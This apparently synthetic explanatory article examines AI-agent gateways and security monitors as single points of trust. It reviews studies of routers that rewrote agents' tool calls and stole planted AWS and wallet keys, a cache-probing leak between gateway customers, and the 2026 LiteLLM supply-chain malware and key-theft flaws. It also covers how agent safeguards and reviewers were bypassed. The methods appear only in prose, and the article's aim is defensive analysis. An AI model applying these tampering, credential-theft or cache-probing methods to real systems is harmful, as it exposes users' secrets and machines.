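# Security monitors that see all AI agent traffic as single points of trust

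## How a monitor of agent traffic comes to hold secrets

An AI agent is a program that runs a language model in a loop. The model proposes an action, the program carries it out, and the result goes back to the model for the next step. Agents read files, run commands and call outside services, often with all the permissions of the person who started them. Many organisations therefore route agent traffic through a monitor, a component that can allow, change, block or record it. To do this, the monitor usually has to read the traffic, which contains secrets. A secret here is any value whose disclosure gives access or does harm, such as a password, an access token, a customer record or an API key (the string that identifies a customer to an online service).

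An organisation installs a monitor for safety, but an attacker who breaks into it can get the secrets of every agent behind it. The damage depends on what information the monitor needs to do its job and what an attacker gains by taking it over.

The most familiar example is the gateway, a proxy that sits where a monitor would, between agents and the model providers (the companies that run the models) or the tools that agents use. Developers mostly adopt gateways for convenience, since they can reach many providers through one address and pay through one account. *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (Fu, Li and colleagues, 2026) puts downloads of the packaged image of LiteLLM, the leading open-source gateway, at more than 240 million.

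### One request, there and back

Suppose a company sends all its agents' requests through a gateway. A developer there asks a coding agent why a program cannot reach its database, and the agent opens a configuration file containing the database password. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (Xie, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes roughly this path.

1. On the developer's machine, the agent adds the file, password included, to the conversation that it will send to the model. It also holds a gateway key, which the gateway's operator issued to the developer. Any program with access to the developer's files and processes can read both.
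2. The agent connects to the gateway over TLS (Transport Layer Security), the protocol that encrypts most web traffic. An eavesdropper on this stretch gets scrambled bytes, plus the size and timing of the messages.
3. Inside the gateway the encrypted connection ends. The instructions, the file, the password and the gateway key are all readable. The gateway checks the gateway key, picks one of the operator's accounts with a provider, and fetches the provider key for that account from its own store. The developer never receives this second key.
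4. The gateway opens a new TLS connection to the provider and sends the request on with the provider key attached. On the wire there are again only scrambled bytes.
5. At the provider the connection ends, and the provider's servers read the whole conversation in order to run the model on it.
6. The reply returns over the same two connections, so it lies open in the gateway as well. It may contain a tool call, a structured instruction for the agent to run something, and here that could be a command with the database password in it. The gateway counts the usage for billing and may write some or all of the exchange to a log.
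7. The agent runs the command and adds the output to its next request. Agents commonly resend the conversation so far each time, so the password makes the same trip again at every later step.

Step 3 is TLS termination, in which an intermediary ends an encrypted connection, reads the content, and opens a second connection onward. This does not require breaking any encryption. TLS protects a connection between two endpoints, and a certificate lets the client check that it has reached the endpoint it wanted. The check succeeds here because the developer entered the gateway's address in the agent's settings, but it does not show what the gateway does next. *Your Agent Is Mine* (Liu, Shou and colleagues, 2026), which tested 428 such gateways for dishonest behaviour, points out that no provider enforces a cryptographic integrity check between the model and the client. An agent therefore cannot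 distinguish the provider's reply from one that the gateway rewrote.

The provider also reads everything, but Xie and colleagues assume it is honest and leave it out of their threat model. This is a sensible way to isolate the problem, because the developer has to show the conversation to some provider anyway, while the gateway is an additional party.

### Complete mediation and its price

The idea that a single mechanism should check everything is much older than AI agents. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, reported to the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. The expert panel behind the study assumed that a legitimate user of the machine might be hostile. It recommended a design built around a reference monitor, which compares every attempt by a program to use data, devices or other programs with a list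 of what that program's user may do. The mechanism that implements it has to meet three requirements:

- Nobody can tamper with it.
- It runs on every access, with no way around it.
- It is small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

Anderson checked GCOS III, an operating system of the time, against this list. The hardware confined a user's program to its own area of memory, but most of the operating system ran with that check suspended, even when acting for a user. The system and its supporting software contained 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many for anyone to verify.

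In *Ring-0 by Default*, Li, Huang and colleagues (2026) applied the same three criteria to current coding agents and found that these also fall short, because safety rules written into a model's instructions meet none of the criteria. The three command-line agents they tested had access checks inside individual tools, so a file write that the file tool refused went through when the agent used the command shell. They conclude that a defence has to be a reference monitor outside the model. This is a good argument for placing a monitor at a point that all traffic must cross, such as a gateway on a network that blocks other routes.

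Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, published three years after Anderson's report, sets out eight design principles for protection mechanisms. One of them, complete mediation, restates Anderson's second requirement that the system check every access to every object for authority. Two others are in tension with it. Under least privilege, every program and user should work with the fewest privileges the job requires, which limits the damage from an accident or error. Under least common mechanism, a system should have as few mechanisms as possible that several users share and all depend on, because every shared mechanism could leak information between them.

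A gateway that serves every agent in a company conflicts with the principle of least common mechanism, because all the agents share it. It conflicts less directly with least privilege. A monitor that must check everything can correctly claim that it needs to see everything, so it complies with the letter of the principle, but the damage from its failure has no useful limit. Anderson had already observed that computers were a "uniquely attractive target" for attackers because they concentrated data and control in one place and their controls could be subverted by programming.

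A monitor may not need to see the contents of agents' requests. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) sets out formal rules for a monitor of agents that probe websites for weaknesses. In its running example, a client permits at most 10,000 requests, which must use the HTTP methods for fetching pages (GET and HEAD) and go only to subdomains of example.com, with the findings sent to one dashboard. To decide on a request, the monitor checks the destination, port, protocol, method, running total, and a label declaring which kind of data is going where, but not the request's contents.

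TLS encrypts the HTTP method. As David and colleagues note, hooks in the operating system's kernel do not by themselves expose it, so the check has to happen in an HTTP proxy or in the agent's own software before encryption. A proxy that decrypts traffic to read the method also holds the passwords and page text in its memory. A wrapper around the agent's tools could send the monitor only the short record, but the wrapper would still handle the contents, so its code would also have to be correct.

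Complete mediation only requires a monitor to check every request, not to read every byte. But ordinary TLS termination decrypts all the traffic, so a monitor that uses it can read everything. Many monitors also need the contents, for instance to catch an agent that is about to send a customer list to a stranger.

### Where the secrets sit, and who can take them

A monitor exposes secrets in its working memory, its permanent storage and its logs, and the amount an attacker can take differs between them. Memory holds whatever traffic is passing through at the moment, so an attacker who can read it collects only what passes while they have access. On a busy gateway, that may include most of the important secrets within a day or so.

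The monitor's storage holds the provider keys, so an attacker who copies it gets all of them, including keys that no agent has used for months. It may also hold detection rules. These can include secrets, such as a list of passwords that the monitor compares with traffic to find leaks. An attacker can learn what to avoid even from rules that contain no secrets.

A password that spends two seconds in memory can stay in a log for a year, and logs tend to end up in backups and search systems where more people can read them. Much of this exposure is avoidable. For instance, the 10,000-request limit in the example above needs only a counter, which contains no passwords.

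The gateway's operator can take these secrets without breaking in. In the threat model of Xie and colleagues, a dishonest operator can run any code in the gateway, read and write its databases, observe all the traffic and choose which account serves each request, so all three places are open from the start. What an outsider can take depends on how they get in. A flaw in the database layer may expose only the stored keys, while control of the running program exposes everything. The distinction between these two attackers is not always clear. Liu and colleagues show that leaked keys and weak configuration can draw ostensibly honest gateways into the same abuse.

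Poisoned software from a supplier can compromise a monitor even when its operators are honest, because it arrives as a normal update and runs with the monitor's own privileges at every customer who installs it. Anderson wrote in 1972 that nobody can certify that an operating system contains no "trap doors" if the manufacturer maintains it, and his plan had vetted people write the security functions in a controlled environment. Most users of open-source gateways have no comparable protection. Fu and colleagues recount that in March 2026 two malicious releases of LiteLLM, one such gateway, harvested credentials from the machines that installed them.

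A captured monitor permits all three kinds of security violation that Saltzer and Schroeder identified: unauthorised release of information, unauthorised modification, and unauthorised denial of use. Modification may be the worst for coding agents, because an altered tool call becomes a command on the developer's machine. Fu and colleagues had a gateway insert malicious actions, at four levels of subtlety, into the replies sent to four widely used coding agents. Without added defences, none of the agents resisted at any level. If the monitor stops working, either every agent behind it stops too or the traffic continues unchecked. Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults, under which a system refuses access unless something explicitly permits it, favours stopping the agents, but this lets anyone who can crash the monitor halt the work.

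### The assumption that the monitor is sound

Designs for agent security tend to treat the agent as untrusted and the monitor as trusted. David and colleagues state this assumption openly. Their central theorem shows that, whatever sequence of actions an agent proposes, the part the monitor lets through always satisfies the contract (the formal version of the client's rules). The proof is a short induction. An empty record satisfies the contract, and the monitor adds an action only if the record still satisfies the contract afterwards. The proof doesn't depend on the model, so it holds even if the model is deceptive or controlled by instructions that an attacker hid in a web page.

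The theorem depends on a monitor that is correctly implemented and that no one has compromised, which David and colleagues call "the standard reference monitor assumption". Their trusted computing base, all the code and hardware that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold, consists of the monitor, the points where it intercepts actions, and the contract. They consider an attacker who controls the website under test, but not a dishonest operator or a compromised supplier.

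Any proof about enforcement must assume something about the enforcer, and this theorem assumes that the monitor has not been compromised. The theorem covers only the agent's actions, and a copy of a password in the monitor's memory is not one of them. A monitor could make every allow-or-deny decision correctly while writing each password to a log that half the company can read, and the theorem would still hold. If an attacker takes over the monitor, the guarantee lapses entirely, and the theory does not measure how much is lost. Two monitors can enforce the same rules equally reliably, yet a takeover would expose far more from one that keeps transcripts than from one that keeps a counter.

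Fu and colleagues found a related gap in the safeguards on the developer's side. Lists of permitted commands and reviews of each reply by a second model both rely on the reply being the one the provider produced, but nobody has checked this when a gateway sits between the developer and the provider.

The assumption was easier to defend in its original setting. Staff with security clearances would have built Anderson's monitor into a computer that the Air Force ran, and his study explicitly left physical security and the protection of communication lines to other measures. In 2026, a gateway may belong to a company the developer knows only by its web address.

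### Hashes, keyed hashes and encryption

If nobody can guarantee that a monitor will stay secure, the alternative is to reduce the number of secrets it could leak. Most attempts to do this rely on a few basic tools.

A hash is a fixed-length value computed from data, easy to compute and infeasible to reverse except by guessing the input. The same input always gives the same hash, so a monitor can store a password's hash and later recognise the password without storing the password itself. Hashes protect long random keys very well but protect short passwords and phone numbers badly, because an attacker can try every possible short input. Saltzer and Schroeder counted 456,976 possible four-letter passwords and considered an attacker whose computer tries a million per second, which would take under half a second to try them all. A random 128-bit key has about 3.4 × 10^38 possible values, and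 trying them all at a trillion guesses per second would take around 10^19 years.

A keyed hash depends on a secret key as well as the input, so a thief who copies only the stored hashes cannot test guesses against them. If the key is stored near the hashes, a thief who finds it can test guesses as with an unkeyed hash. An attacker who controls the running monitor may not need to find the key, because the monitor must be able to compute keyed hashes of live traffic and the attacker can feed it guesses.

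Encryption, which Saltzer and Schroeder call encipherment, scrambles data under a secret key so that it can be sent through or stored in an unprotected place, and whoever holds the right key can normally reverse it. In the request above, the gateway only has to recognise the developer's gateway key, so a hash is enough. But it has to send the provider key onward in its original form, so the running gateway must have access to the means of decrypting it. Encrypted storage therefore protects the provider key from someone who steals a copy of the database, but does very little against someone who is running code in the gateway itself.

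## Dishonest gateways: a test of 428 model routers

Hashing and encryption give little protection against a gateway's own operator. In April 2026, Liu and colleagues published a test of 428 public gateways, which they describe as the first systematic study of dishonest operators. They call such gateways routers, and some later researchers call them relays.

The researchers bought access to 28 paid routers on the Chinese marketplaces Taobao and Xianyu and from Shopify stores. They collected the other 400, all free, from public online communities. According to *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet* (2026), a blog post covering the full paper, two open-source templates account for most of the free routers. Routers are especially common in regions where direct access to a provider is expensive or restricted.

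A request may pass through more routers than the customer knows about. In the paper's example, a developer buys access from a reseller on Taobao, who buys it from an aggregator. The aggregator goes through OpenRouter, a large commercial router, which sends the request to the company running the model. Everyone in this chain can read and change the traffic, but the developer chose only the reseller.

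### How planted credentials reveal theft

A router can copy a password and still pass the traffic on unchanged, so the customer sees nothing wrong. To catch this, Liu and colleagues sent canary credentials through the routers. A canary is a credential that its owner never uses, so any use of it means someone else has a copy. Some of the canaries were access keys for Amazon Web Services (AWS), a cloud platform where owners can see when their keys are used. Another was the private key to a wallet holding a little of the cryptocurrency ether (ETH), which anyone with the key could spend.

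The blog post describes the procedure for each router:

1. The researchers opened an account and obtained a key.
2. They connected a coding agent to the router from inside a sandbox, an isolated environment where malicious code can do no harm. The agent worked on a random selection of tasks, some from TerminalBench 2.0, a public collection of command-line exercises. These tasks naturally lead to shell commands, software installations and file changes.
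3. They executed every tool call that came back, while the sandbox watched for unexpected network connections, file changes and processes.
4. A second agent reviewed the suspicious runs and sorted them into harmless rewriting, potentially malicious and confirmed malicious.

A router counted as injecting malicious code only if it rewrote a tool call into a command or software package that an attacker controls. Reformatting a reply did not count. A router counted as touching an AWS canary only if there was AWS activity under that key after the key had passed through the router.

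The credential test probably misses some thieves. An operator who stores keys and sells them a year later looks honest, as does one who suspects bait and leaves it alone. A positive result is better evidence of theft somewhere along the route than of theft by the router's seller, because a thief further along the chain would make the first router look guilty.

### What the routers did

| Behaviour | Paid routers (28) | Free routers (400) |
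|---|---|---|
| Injected malicious code into tool calls | 1 | 8 |
| Used a planted AWS key | 0 | 17 |
| Emptied the planted Ethereum wallet | 0 | 1 |

Some of the routers that injected code did so only under certain conditions, so passing a short test does not prove that a router is honest.

The paid routers appear less likely to misuse credentials, but the sample is too small to establish this. If paid routers used stolen AWS keys at the same rate as free ones (about 4%), there would still be a roughly 30% chance that none in a random sample of 28 did so.

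The theft from the wallet cost the researchers less than $50, money they had put there as bait. The OECD's *Malicious AI Routers Enable Cryptocurrency and Credential Theft*, an AI-generated entry in a public database of AI incidents, still classifies the study as an incident with actual harm to property.

Later accounts give different totals. Fu and colleagues write that 18 routers abused credentials, without explaining the figure. They probably added the router that emptied the wallet to the 17 that used AWS keys, which is correct only if it was not one of the 17. Risky Bulletin's *Malicious LLM proxy routers found in the wild* reports 28 malicious routers, apparently by adding the nine that injected code, the 17 that used AWS keys, and two that delayed their attacks, but those two were already among the nine. Depending on how the groups overlap, between 18 and 27 different routers misbehaved,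 or 4% to 6% of the sample.

These rates do not apply to a security monitor that a company runs itself. Most of the routers came from Chinese-language marketplaces and communities. The test excluded enterprise and invitation-only services, and it did not cover LiteLLM or OpenRouter. A company's security team also has much less reason to steal the company's keys than an anonymous reseller does. However, a company monitor that decrypts traffic occupies the same position as these routers, so an attacker who took it over could do what their operators did, probably with more valuable credentials.

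### How honest routers expose their customers

An honest operator can still send customers' traffic to a stranger. Liu and colleagues demonstrated this in two experiments that they call poisoning studies.

In the first, they deliberately leaked one of their own OpenAI keys on Chinese forums and in WeChat and Telegram groups that router operators frequent. Other people used it to generate 100 million GPT-5.4 tokens (the fragments of text that models process and providers bill for). The traffic exposed more than seven sessions of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The provider's logs did not always show whether a router operator, an unrelated person or a longer chain of routers had used the key. In any of these cases, the end users would have had no way of knowing whose key they were using.

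In the second experiment, the researchers set up decoy routers that were easy to break into. Those at 20 web domains ran vulnerable software, and those at 20 internet addresses had weak passwords. The decoys received more than 40,000 unauthorised access attempts from 147 addresses. Many of these may have been automated scans, but other people then used the decoys in working routes for agents.

The decoys handled about 2 billion billed tokens and about 13 gigabytes of readable prompts and replies. This traffic contained 99 different credentials and came from 440 Codex sessions across 398 projects or machines. In 401 of those sessions, the agent ran commands without asking for approval. The researchers could have inserted a command into any of the 440 sessions, and a simple insertion would have been enough in the 401 that ran without approval. They kept only aggregate data and hashes with a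 random value mixed in.

These sessions belonged to real users, who may never have heard of the decoys. Checking that the first operator is honest is therefore not enough, because that operator may be buying capacity from someone careless or unknowingly using a stolen key.

### Three defences on the customer's side

Liu and colleagues also built a router that carries out the attacks and used it to test three defences that a customer can install without the provider's help. The blog post reports the figures below from the full paper, and they come from artificial examples that the researchers generated.

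The first defence, a policy gate, blocks any shell command that downloads from a website or installs a software package outside an approved list. In a test of 1,000 harmless and 1,000 malicious commands, it blocked all of the malicious ones and only 1% of the harmless ones. But an attacker who knew about the gate and kept within the approved list got past it every time. Liu and colleagues consider it the strongest defence available today, but useful mainly against obvious attacks.

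Anomaly screening gives each returned tool call a score based on features such as risky shell patterns. It flagged 89% of ordinary injections, but only 50% of injections that swapped one software package for another. It also flagged 6.7% of harmless calls. When the researchers adjusted it to flag no more than 1% of harmless calls, it caught 43.5% of ordinary injections and almost none of the package swaps.

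The third defence is an append-only log, in which software can add entries but not change old ones. It records each request and response, the router's address and a hash of the raw response. Each entry takes about 1.26 kilobytes. The log helps a customer work out after an attack which sessions and credentials a bad router saw, but it does not stop the attack. The blog post advises removing secrets from requests before logging them.

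None of the three defenses protects a secret that the agent has already sent. The gate and the screening examine the reply. By then, the router has read the request and may have copied any password in it. The log only shows which password to replace.

Liu and colleagues propose that the provider sign each response. The signature would cover the model's name, the tool call and its arguments, and a one-time value from the client. A client could then detect a rewritten command before running it, but the router would still see the request. Protecting the request means keeping secrets out of it or preventing the router's operator from reading it. Xie and colleagues attempt the latter with attested hardware.

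### How the defences fared in July

In their tampering experiment of July 2026, Fu and colleagues also tried similar defences, with much worse results. They wrote 400 malicious tool calls and inserted each into three coding tasks, making 1,200 attacks per setting. An approved list of websites and packages stopped only 31% to 44% of them. Much of the difference from the April result probably comes from the choice of attacks. Liu and colleagues tested the gate on unapproved downloads and installations, which are what it checks for. A quarter of the attacks in the July test planted bugs in the developer's code, which need not involve a download.

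A second AI model that reviewed each call before execution did somewhat better, stopping 39% to 64% of attacks depending on the model and the type of injection. Between 9% and 53% of the calls it blocked were harmless. The reviewer needed its own direct connection to a provider. The agents' built-in reviews stopped no attacks because the review requests went through the same dishonest router. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a planning mode that is supposed to be read-only, but this restriction is only an instruction to the model, so the agent still ran the router's inserted commands in that mode.

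Developers might not notice the attacks from the finished work. Across four models used behind Claude Code, the attacks lowered the task success rate by about 1 to 7 percentage points. The test covered only three tasks, so these percentages may not hold elsewhere. It also did not measure how common dishonest routers are, because the researchers controlled the router.

### A second sample of relays

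In *What the Middleman Delivers*, Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) tested 20 commercial relays in two rounds in October 2026. Most of the relays had an English interface and accepted a credit card or PayPal, so the sample came from a different part of the market. The researchers sent harmless requests for code and setup instructions and found no confirmed malicious injection in 3,332 responses.

This does not contradict the April result. The responses came from only 20 relays, and if 2% of relays injected code, as in April, a random sample of 20 would include no relays that do so about two-thirds of the time. The researchers also never ran a returned command, so they could have missed attacks that begin only once an agent is using tools. They sent no secrets and did not test whether relays store or misuse credentials, so their results cannot confirm or refute the April figure for stolen keys.

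They did find other irregularities. In the first round, four relays returned tool calls even though the request had disabled tools, and most of the calls came from one relay. None did so in the second round.

Five relays reported between 4,200 and 60,000 more input tokens than the official service for the same request. For one question, the official count was 36 tokens and three relays reported about 4,400. Hidden instructions added to the customer's request would explain this, but so would inaccurate accounting, and the customer cannot tell which. At one of the five, account balances confirmed that the customer paid for the extra tokens.

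A higher price did not reliably indicate better service. Seven of the ten cheap relays and two of the ten others gave answers that differed measurably from the official model's, but a gap this large could plausibly arise by chance (p = 0.07).

### When another customer is the spy

A shared gateway can leak information even when its operator is honest. To save work, model providers keep the results of processing the beginning of a long prompt and reuse them when another prompt begins the same way. This is called prompt caching, and the reply reports how many tokens came from the cache. Providers keep different customers' caches separate, but if a gateway sends all its customers' requests through one provider account, those customers share a cache.

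Sun, Cai and colleagues (2026), in *KeyPooling*, tested for this leak with four requests from two accounts on the same gateway, here called Alice and Bob:

1. Alice sends a long random text, and the reply reports no cached tokens.
2. Bob sends the same text. If the reply reports cached tokens, he has learned that someone else already sent it.
3. Alice repeats her text, to check that the cache is still working.
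4. Bob sends an unrelated text, which should report no cached tokens.

The researchers ran this on five open-source gateways connected to OpenAI and Anthropic. None gave each customer a separate provider credential by default, and all five leaked with both providers when customers shared a credential. On OpenRouter, the leak appeared for 12 of the 28 model labels tested, which carried about a third of the volume.

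The basic attack works only if Bob already has the text. He can confirm that someone on the gateway is using a confidential document, but not who. Under favourable conditions, he can also guess a continuation one token at a time, checking each guess against the cache count. On one live route, the researchers recovered eight consecutive tokens of a planted text this way, although the text had only 65,536 possible values. Coding agents make the attack easier because their prompts usually begin with long public instructions that already meet the minimum length for caching.

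This finding is more relevant to companies than the theft rates from April, because a company can install the same open-source gateways for its own staff. A contractor with a gateway key might check whether the legal department had sent a particular draft contract to a model. Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of least common mechanism was meant to prevent this sort of leak.

One solution is to give each customer a separate account with its own cache, but providers limit how many accounts a gateway can have. OpenAI separates caches by organisation and does not offer additional organisations through self-service. Anthropic's direct service separates them by workspace and allows 100 workspaces per organisation. Sun and colleagues suggest that the gateway could instead add a label derived from the customer's login to each prompt, so that different customers' prompts no longer match. Placing the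 label after the shared public instructions preserves most of the savings from caching, and they estimate that costs rise by only 1.7% to 2.5%.

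## LiteLLM in 2026: attacks on a gateway that stores provider keys

A company that runs its own gateway doesn't have to trust a reseller, but it must still trust the gateway's software. Attackers published malicious versions of LiteLLM, the most popular choice, in March and October 2026. Researchers also found several flaws that year that let strangers or ordinary users access the keys it stores.

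LiteLLM is both a library and a gateway, and the attacks affected the two differently. According to LiteLLM's documentation, the library lets Python programs call more than 100 language models in OpenAI's format. A program that uses it this way needs only its own keys. The same Python package also contains the gateway, usually called the proxy, which a whole organisation can share. Programmers install the package from the Python Package Index (PyPI), the main public source of Python software. The proxy also comes as a Docker image, which bundles a program with everything it needs to run.

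A working proxy holds several kinds of secrets:

- The provider keys. The security vendor Penligent, summarising research by Obsidian Security, lists keys for OpenAI, Anthropic, Gemini, Bedrock and Azure, plus any other provider the organisation has set up.
- The virtual keys, LiteLLM's name for the gateway keys that it issues to developers.
- The master key, which gives an administrator control of the proxy.
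- The salt key, with which the proxy encrypts the provider keys in its database.
- The address of that database, normally with its password.

### March: a security scanner leaks the publishing token

The March attack started with Trivy, Aqua Security's open-source scanner that checks software for known vulnerabilities. On 19 March, a criminal group called TeamPCP used one of Aqua's automated accounts to publish a poisoned version. According to BoostSecurity Labs' *TeamPCP Compromises LiteLLM* (2026), the group also changed 75 of the 76 version labels of the component that runs Trivy in GitHub's build service. Projects that specified an older version by one of these labels then got the poisoned one.

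LiteLLM ran Trivy in its automated build system. Dholakia and Jaff (2026), in *Security Townhall Updates*, identify three weaknesses that let the scanner reach LiteLLM's publishing credentials. All the build steps shared one environment, the credentials were stored there permanently, and LiteLLM had not pinned the build to a specific version of Trivy. The scanner needed to read only LiteLLM's code, but it could also read the token used to publish to PyPI. Trend Micro, citing an analysis by the security company CrowdStrike, reports that the real scan still ran after the theft and produced normal output, so the scanner gave no sign of trouble.

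The attackers used the stolen token to upload two versions of LiteLLM directly to PyPI on 24 March, 1.82.7 at 10:39 UTC and 1.82.8 at 10:52. HiddenLayer's *LiteLLM Supply Chain Attack* (2026) reports malicious code in the proxy's main file in both versions. This code ran only when a program loaded the proxy. Version 1.82.8 also contained a file that Python runs every time it starts, so it affected any machine with the package installed, even if nobody used the proxy.

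FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) describes what the malware took:

1. It collected the keys for logging in to other machines, cloud credentials, database passwords, cryptocurrency wallets, and the settings files and environment variables where developers often keep API keys.
2. It encrypted everything and sent it to a web domain that looked like LiteLLM's but had nothing to do with the company.
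3. If the machine belonged to a Kubernetes cluster, a group of machines that run programs together, it tried to read all the cluster's secrets and install a permanent back door on every machine.

An engineer at FutureSearch found the malware by accident. A code editor plugin had installed LiteLLM as a dependency, and a bug made the malware start copies of itself until the computer crashed. When users discussed the attack in a thread on LiteLLM's GitHub page, hundreds of bots flooded the thread, and the owner's account closed it.

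The malware could reach everything on an infected machine. It could steal provider keys from the environment variables of a proxy installed from PyPI, or a single key from a settings file on a laptop. It did not need to read any agent traffic, so the gateway's position made no difference to how the theft worked. The proxy's official Docker image was unaffected because, according to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), its build uses fixed versions of its dependencies.

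### How long the March versions were available, and whose data leaked

Accounts of the exposure time differ. LiteLLM put it at about 40 minutes. FutureSearch's *LiteLLM Hack* gives 46 minutes, with PyPI blocking the package at 11:25 UTC. Red Sky Alliance's *LiteLLM PYTHON* (2026), which reproduces a report by the security company Snyk, gives about three hours.

PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) gives 2 hours and 32 minutes. This is the figure to use because PyPI's staff handled the reports and have the records. The shorter figures cannot be right, because the same report says PyPI received the first warning 1 hour and 19 minutes after the upload. On FutureSearch's timeline, the package would already have been gone for half an hour by then.

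The download counts differ for the same reason. FutureSearch counted 46,996 downloads of the malicious versions in the 46 minutes it measured, while PyPI counted more than 119,000 over the full period. The rates are similar, at roughly 1,000 and 800 downloads a minute. Neither figure is a count of victims, since an automated build system may download the same package many times a day.

It is less clear how much data the attackers got through LiteLLM. In August, the security company Hudson Rock analysed a 153-gigabyte archive of stolen data and linked it to 2,488 corporate domains, including those of AWS, Samsung, Cisco and Salesforce. Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* attributes the archive to the March attack on LiteLLM.

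Some of the data may have come from the Trivy attack. Akamai (2026) notes that the poisoned versions of LiteLLM and Trivy carried the same credential stealer, and Snyk's *How a Poisoned Security Scanner Became the Key to Backdooring LiteLLM* adds that both sent their data to the same infrastructure. Data from the two attacks could therefore have ended up in one archive, and Help Net Security gives no breakdown. The number of companies that lost data through LiteLLM may be well below 2,488. Probably far fewer lost it from a LiteLLM gateway, because one developer's laptop could be enough to put a company on the list.

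### April: a way in through the key check

The proxy checks the virtual key on each request by looking it up in its database. In versions 1.81.16 to 1.83.6, it pasted whatever the caller sent as a key directly into the text of the database query. An attacker could therefore send database commands instead of a key, and the database would run them. This SQL injection flaw is catalogued as CVE-2026-42208.

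The attacker did not need an account because the flaw was in the code that checks whether a requester has one. A monitor that checks every request must also process requests from strangers, so anyone who can connect can reach a flaw in this code. Penligent gives the official severity score as 9.3 out of 10.

A month earlier, on 27 March, Dholakia and Jaff had written that their investigation had found no way to attack the proxy without logging in. The versions then in use already contained this flaw. LiteLLM and an outside firm had checked the last 20 releases for signs of tampering, but such a check would not reveal a programming mistake.

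LiteLLM fixed the flaw in version 1.83.7 and then published a security advisory. According to Penligent, the cloud security company Sysdig saw the first attempts to exploit the flaw 36 hours and 7 minutes after the advisory appeared in GitHub's global database. The attackers went after the valuable parts of LiteLLM's database rather than just running a generic scanning tool, so they had apparently studied how the database was organised. It is unclear how many of the attempts succeeded.

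Unlike the March attack, this one exploited the concentration of keys. The attacker could reach a whole organisation's provider keys without accessing any developer's machine. Encryption may have limited the damage, because the salt key is normally kept outside the database. The attack did not involve live traffic, so a key store that never handled prompts would have been just as attractive a target.

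### Two flaws for anyone with an account

Later in the year, the security company Check Point described two more flaws. Both required a login, but the least powerful account was enough.

| Flaw | What the attacker needed | What the attacker could get | Severity | Fixed in version |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2026-42208 | A connection to the proxy | Contents of the database | 9.3 | 1.83.7 |
| CVE-2026-35029 | Any account | Administrator functions, files, control of the server | 8.7 | 1.83.0 (LiteLLM) or 1.83.9 (Check Point) |
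| CVE-2026-59823 | Any account | Provider keys | 5.3 | 1.83.9 |

CVE-2026-35029 let a user with read-only access change the proxy's central settings. According to ITPro's *LiteLLM flaws allow full admin control and API-key theft*, the user could then read files on the server, replace the administrator's credentials and lock the administrator out, and make the proxy download and run new code. At that point the attacker has all the secrets listed above and can also read and change live traffic.

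The second flaw, CVE-2026-59823, let a user tell the proxy to send a request to a server of the user's choice. The proxy attached the organisation's provider key, as it does for any outgoing request, so the attacker received the key. Encrypting the stored keys does not prevent this. TechRadar's *Security flaws found in top open source AI gateway* reports a severity score of 5.3, or "medium", which seems low for a flaw that exposes the most valuable thing the gateway stores.

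Sources disagree about which version fixed CVE-2026-35029. LiteLLM (2026) announced in April that version 1.83.0 fixed the flaw, but Check Point later told users that all versions before 1.83.9 had both this flaw and the SQL injection. Check Point may have simply given the first version that fixed both, or the April fix may have been incomplete. Either way, the safe choice is version 1.83.9 or later, which fixes both flaws.

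Some organisations may not know that they need to upgrade. Cybernews' *Hackers could steal OpenAI, Anthropic keys through LiteLLM bugs* reports Check Point's warning that many other AI platforms have LiteLLM built in, so it can be running where nobody deliberately installed it.

An attacker who controls the gateway can also use it to control the agents behind it. Obsidian Security's *Breaking LiteLLM* describes another route from an ordinary account to running code on the server, using three other flaws. Its researchers started from prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in a web page or document and hopes the model will follow them, and asked whether an attacker could change the model's reply directly instead. Someone who controls the gateway can, as in the tampering experiments by Fu and colleagues. This attack depends on the gateway's position between the agent and the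 model.

### October: LiteLLM's own pipeline publishes malware

After March, LiteLLM made its release process much stricter. According to IT-Administrator's *LiteLLM*, the new measures included signed Docker images and a rule that only an account tied to one office laptop could publish a release. LiteLLM also adopted Trusted Publishers, a PyPI feature that replaces permanent publishing tokens with short-lived ones for an approved build process.

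On 21 October, this process built, signed and published a malicious version, 1.107.0. LiteLLM's root cause analysis appeared two days later. The Vanguard USA (2026) gives this account of it:

1. On 27 May, a configuration file went into one of LiteLLM's public code repositories. It contained the master key to a deployment of the LiteLLM Agent Platform, an experimental service. The team noticed and marked the exposed keys for revocation, but nobody revoked the master key.
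2. On 10 October, the attacker used this key to enter the platform and extract a GitHub token. The platform used the token to propose code changes. But the token belonged to the owner of LiteLLM's GitHub organisation and gave full access to every repository.
3. The attacker added code that made the automated build system send out its secrets. This produced similar tokens for two engineers.
4. Earlier in the week of the release, LiteLLM had relaxed the rule about the special account. Any two engineers could now start and approve a release between them.
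5. The attacker started the release with one stolen token and approved it with another.

LiteLLM gave a different explanation on the day of the attack. It believed then that the tokens came from the logs of an internal deployment, and that the attacker had probably entered that deployment through a recently patched flaw. LiteLLM (2026) has since said that parts of its early updates were inaccurate or incomplete, and it calls its later analysis the "canonical source of truth". Many news reports from that week still give the first explanation.

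The two-person rule failed because one attacker held both people's tokens. Signature checks didn't stop the attack either, since the signatures only showed that the files came from LiteLLM's pipeline, and the files did come from there. In March, FutureSearch had argued that Trusted Publishers would have prevented the first attack because the attacker would also have had to take over the build process. In October, the attacker did take over the build process.

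The most avoidable mistake, apart from the forgotten revocation, was the choice of token. A service that proposes code changes does not need write access to every repository. Under Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of least privilege, the service would have had its own account with narrow permissions, and the leaked master key would have exposed much less.

### What the October malware looked for

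PyPI offered version 1.107.0 from 11:39 to about 13:20 UTC. The cloud security company Wiz estimated about 49,000 downloads. This time the official Docker images were also malicious, from 11:46 to 14:20, including those with the general labels many users rely on to get the newest version. The attack therefore reached users who run LiteLLM as a gateway from its official image, who had been safe in March. Customers using LiteLLM's private enterprise release were not affected.

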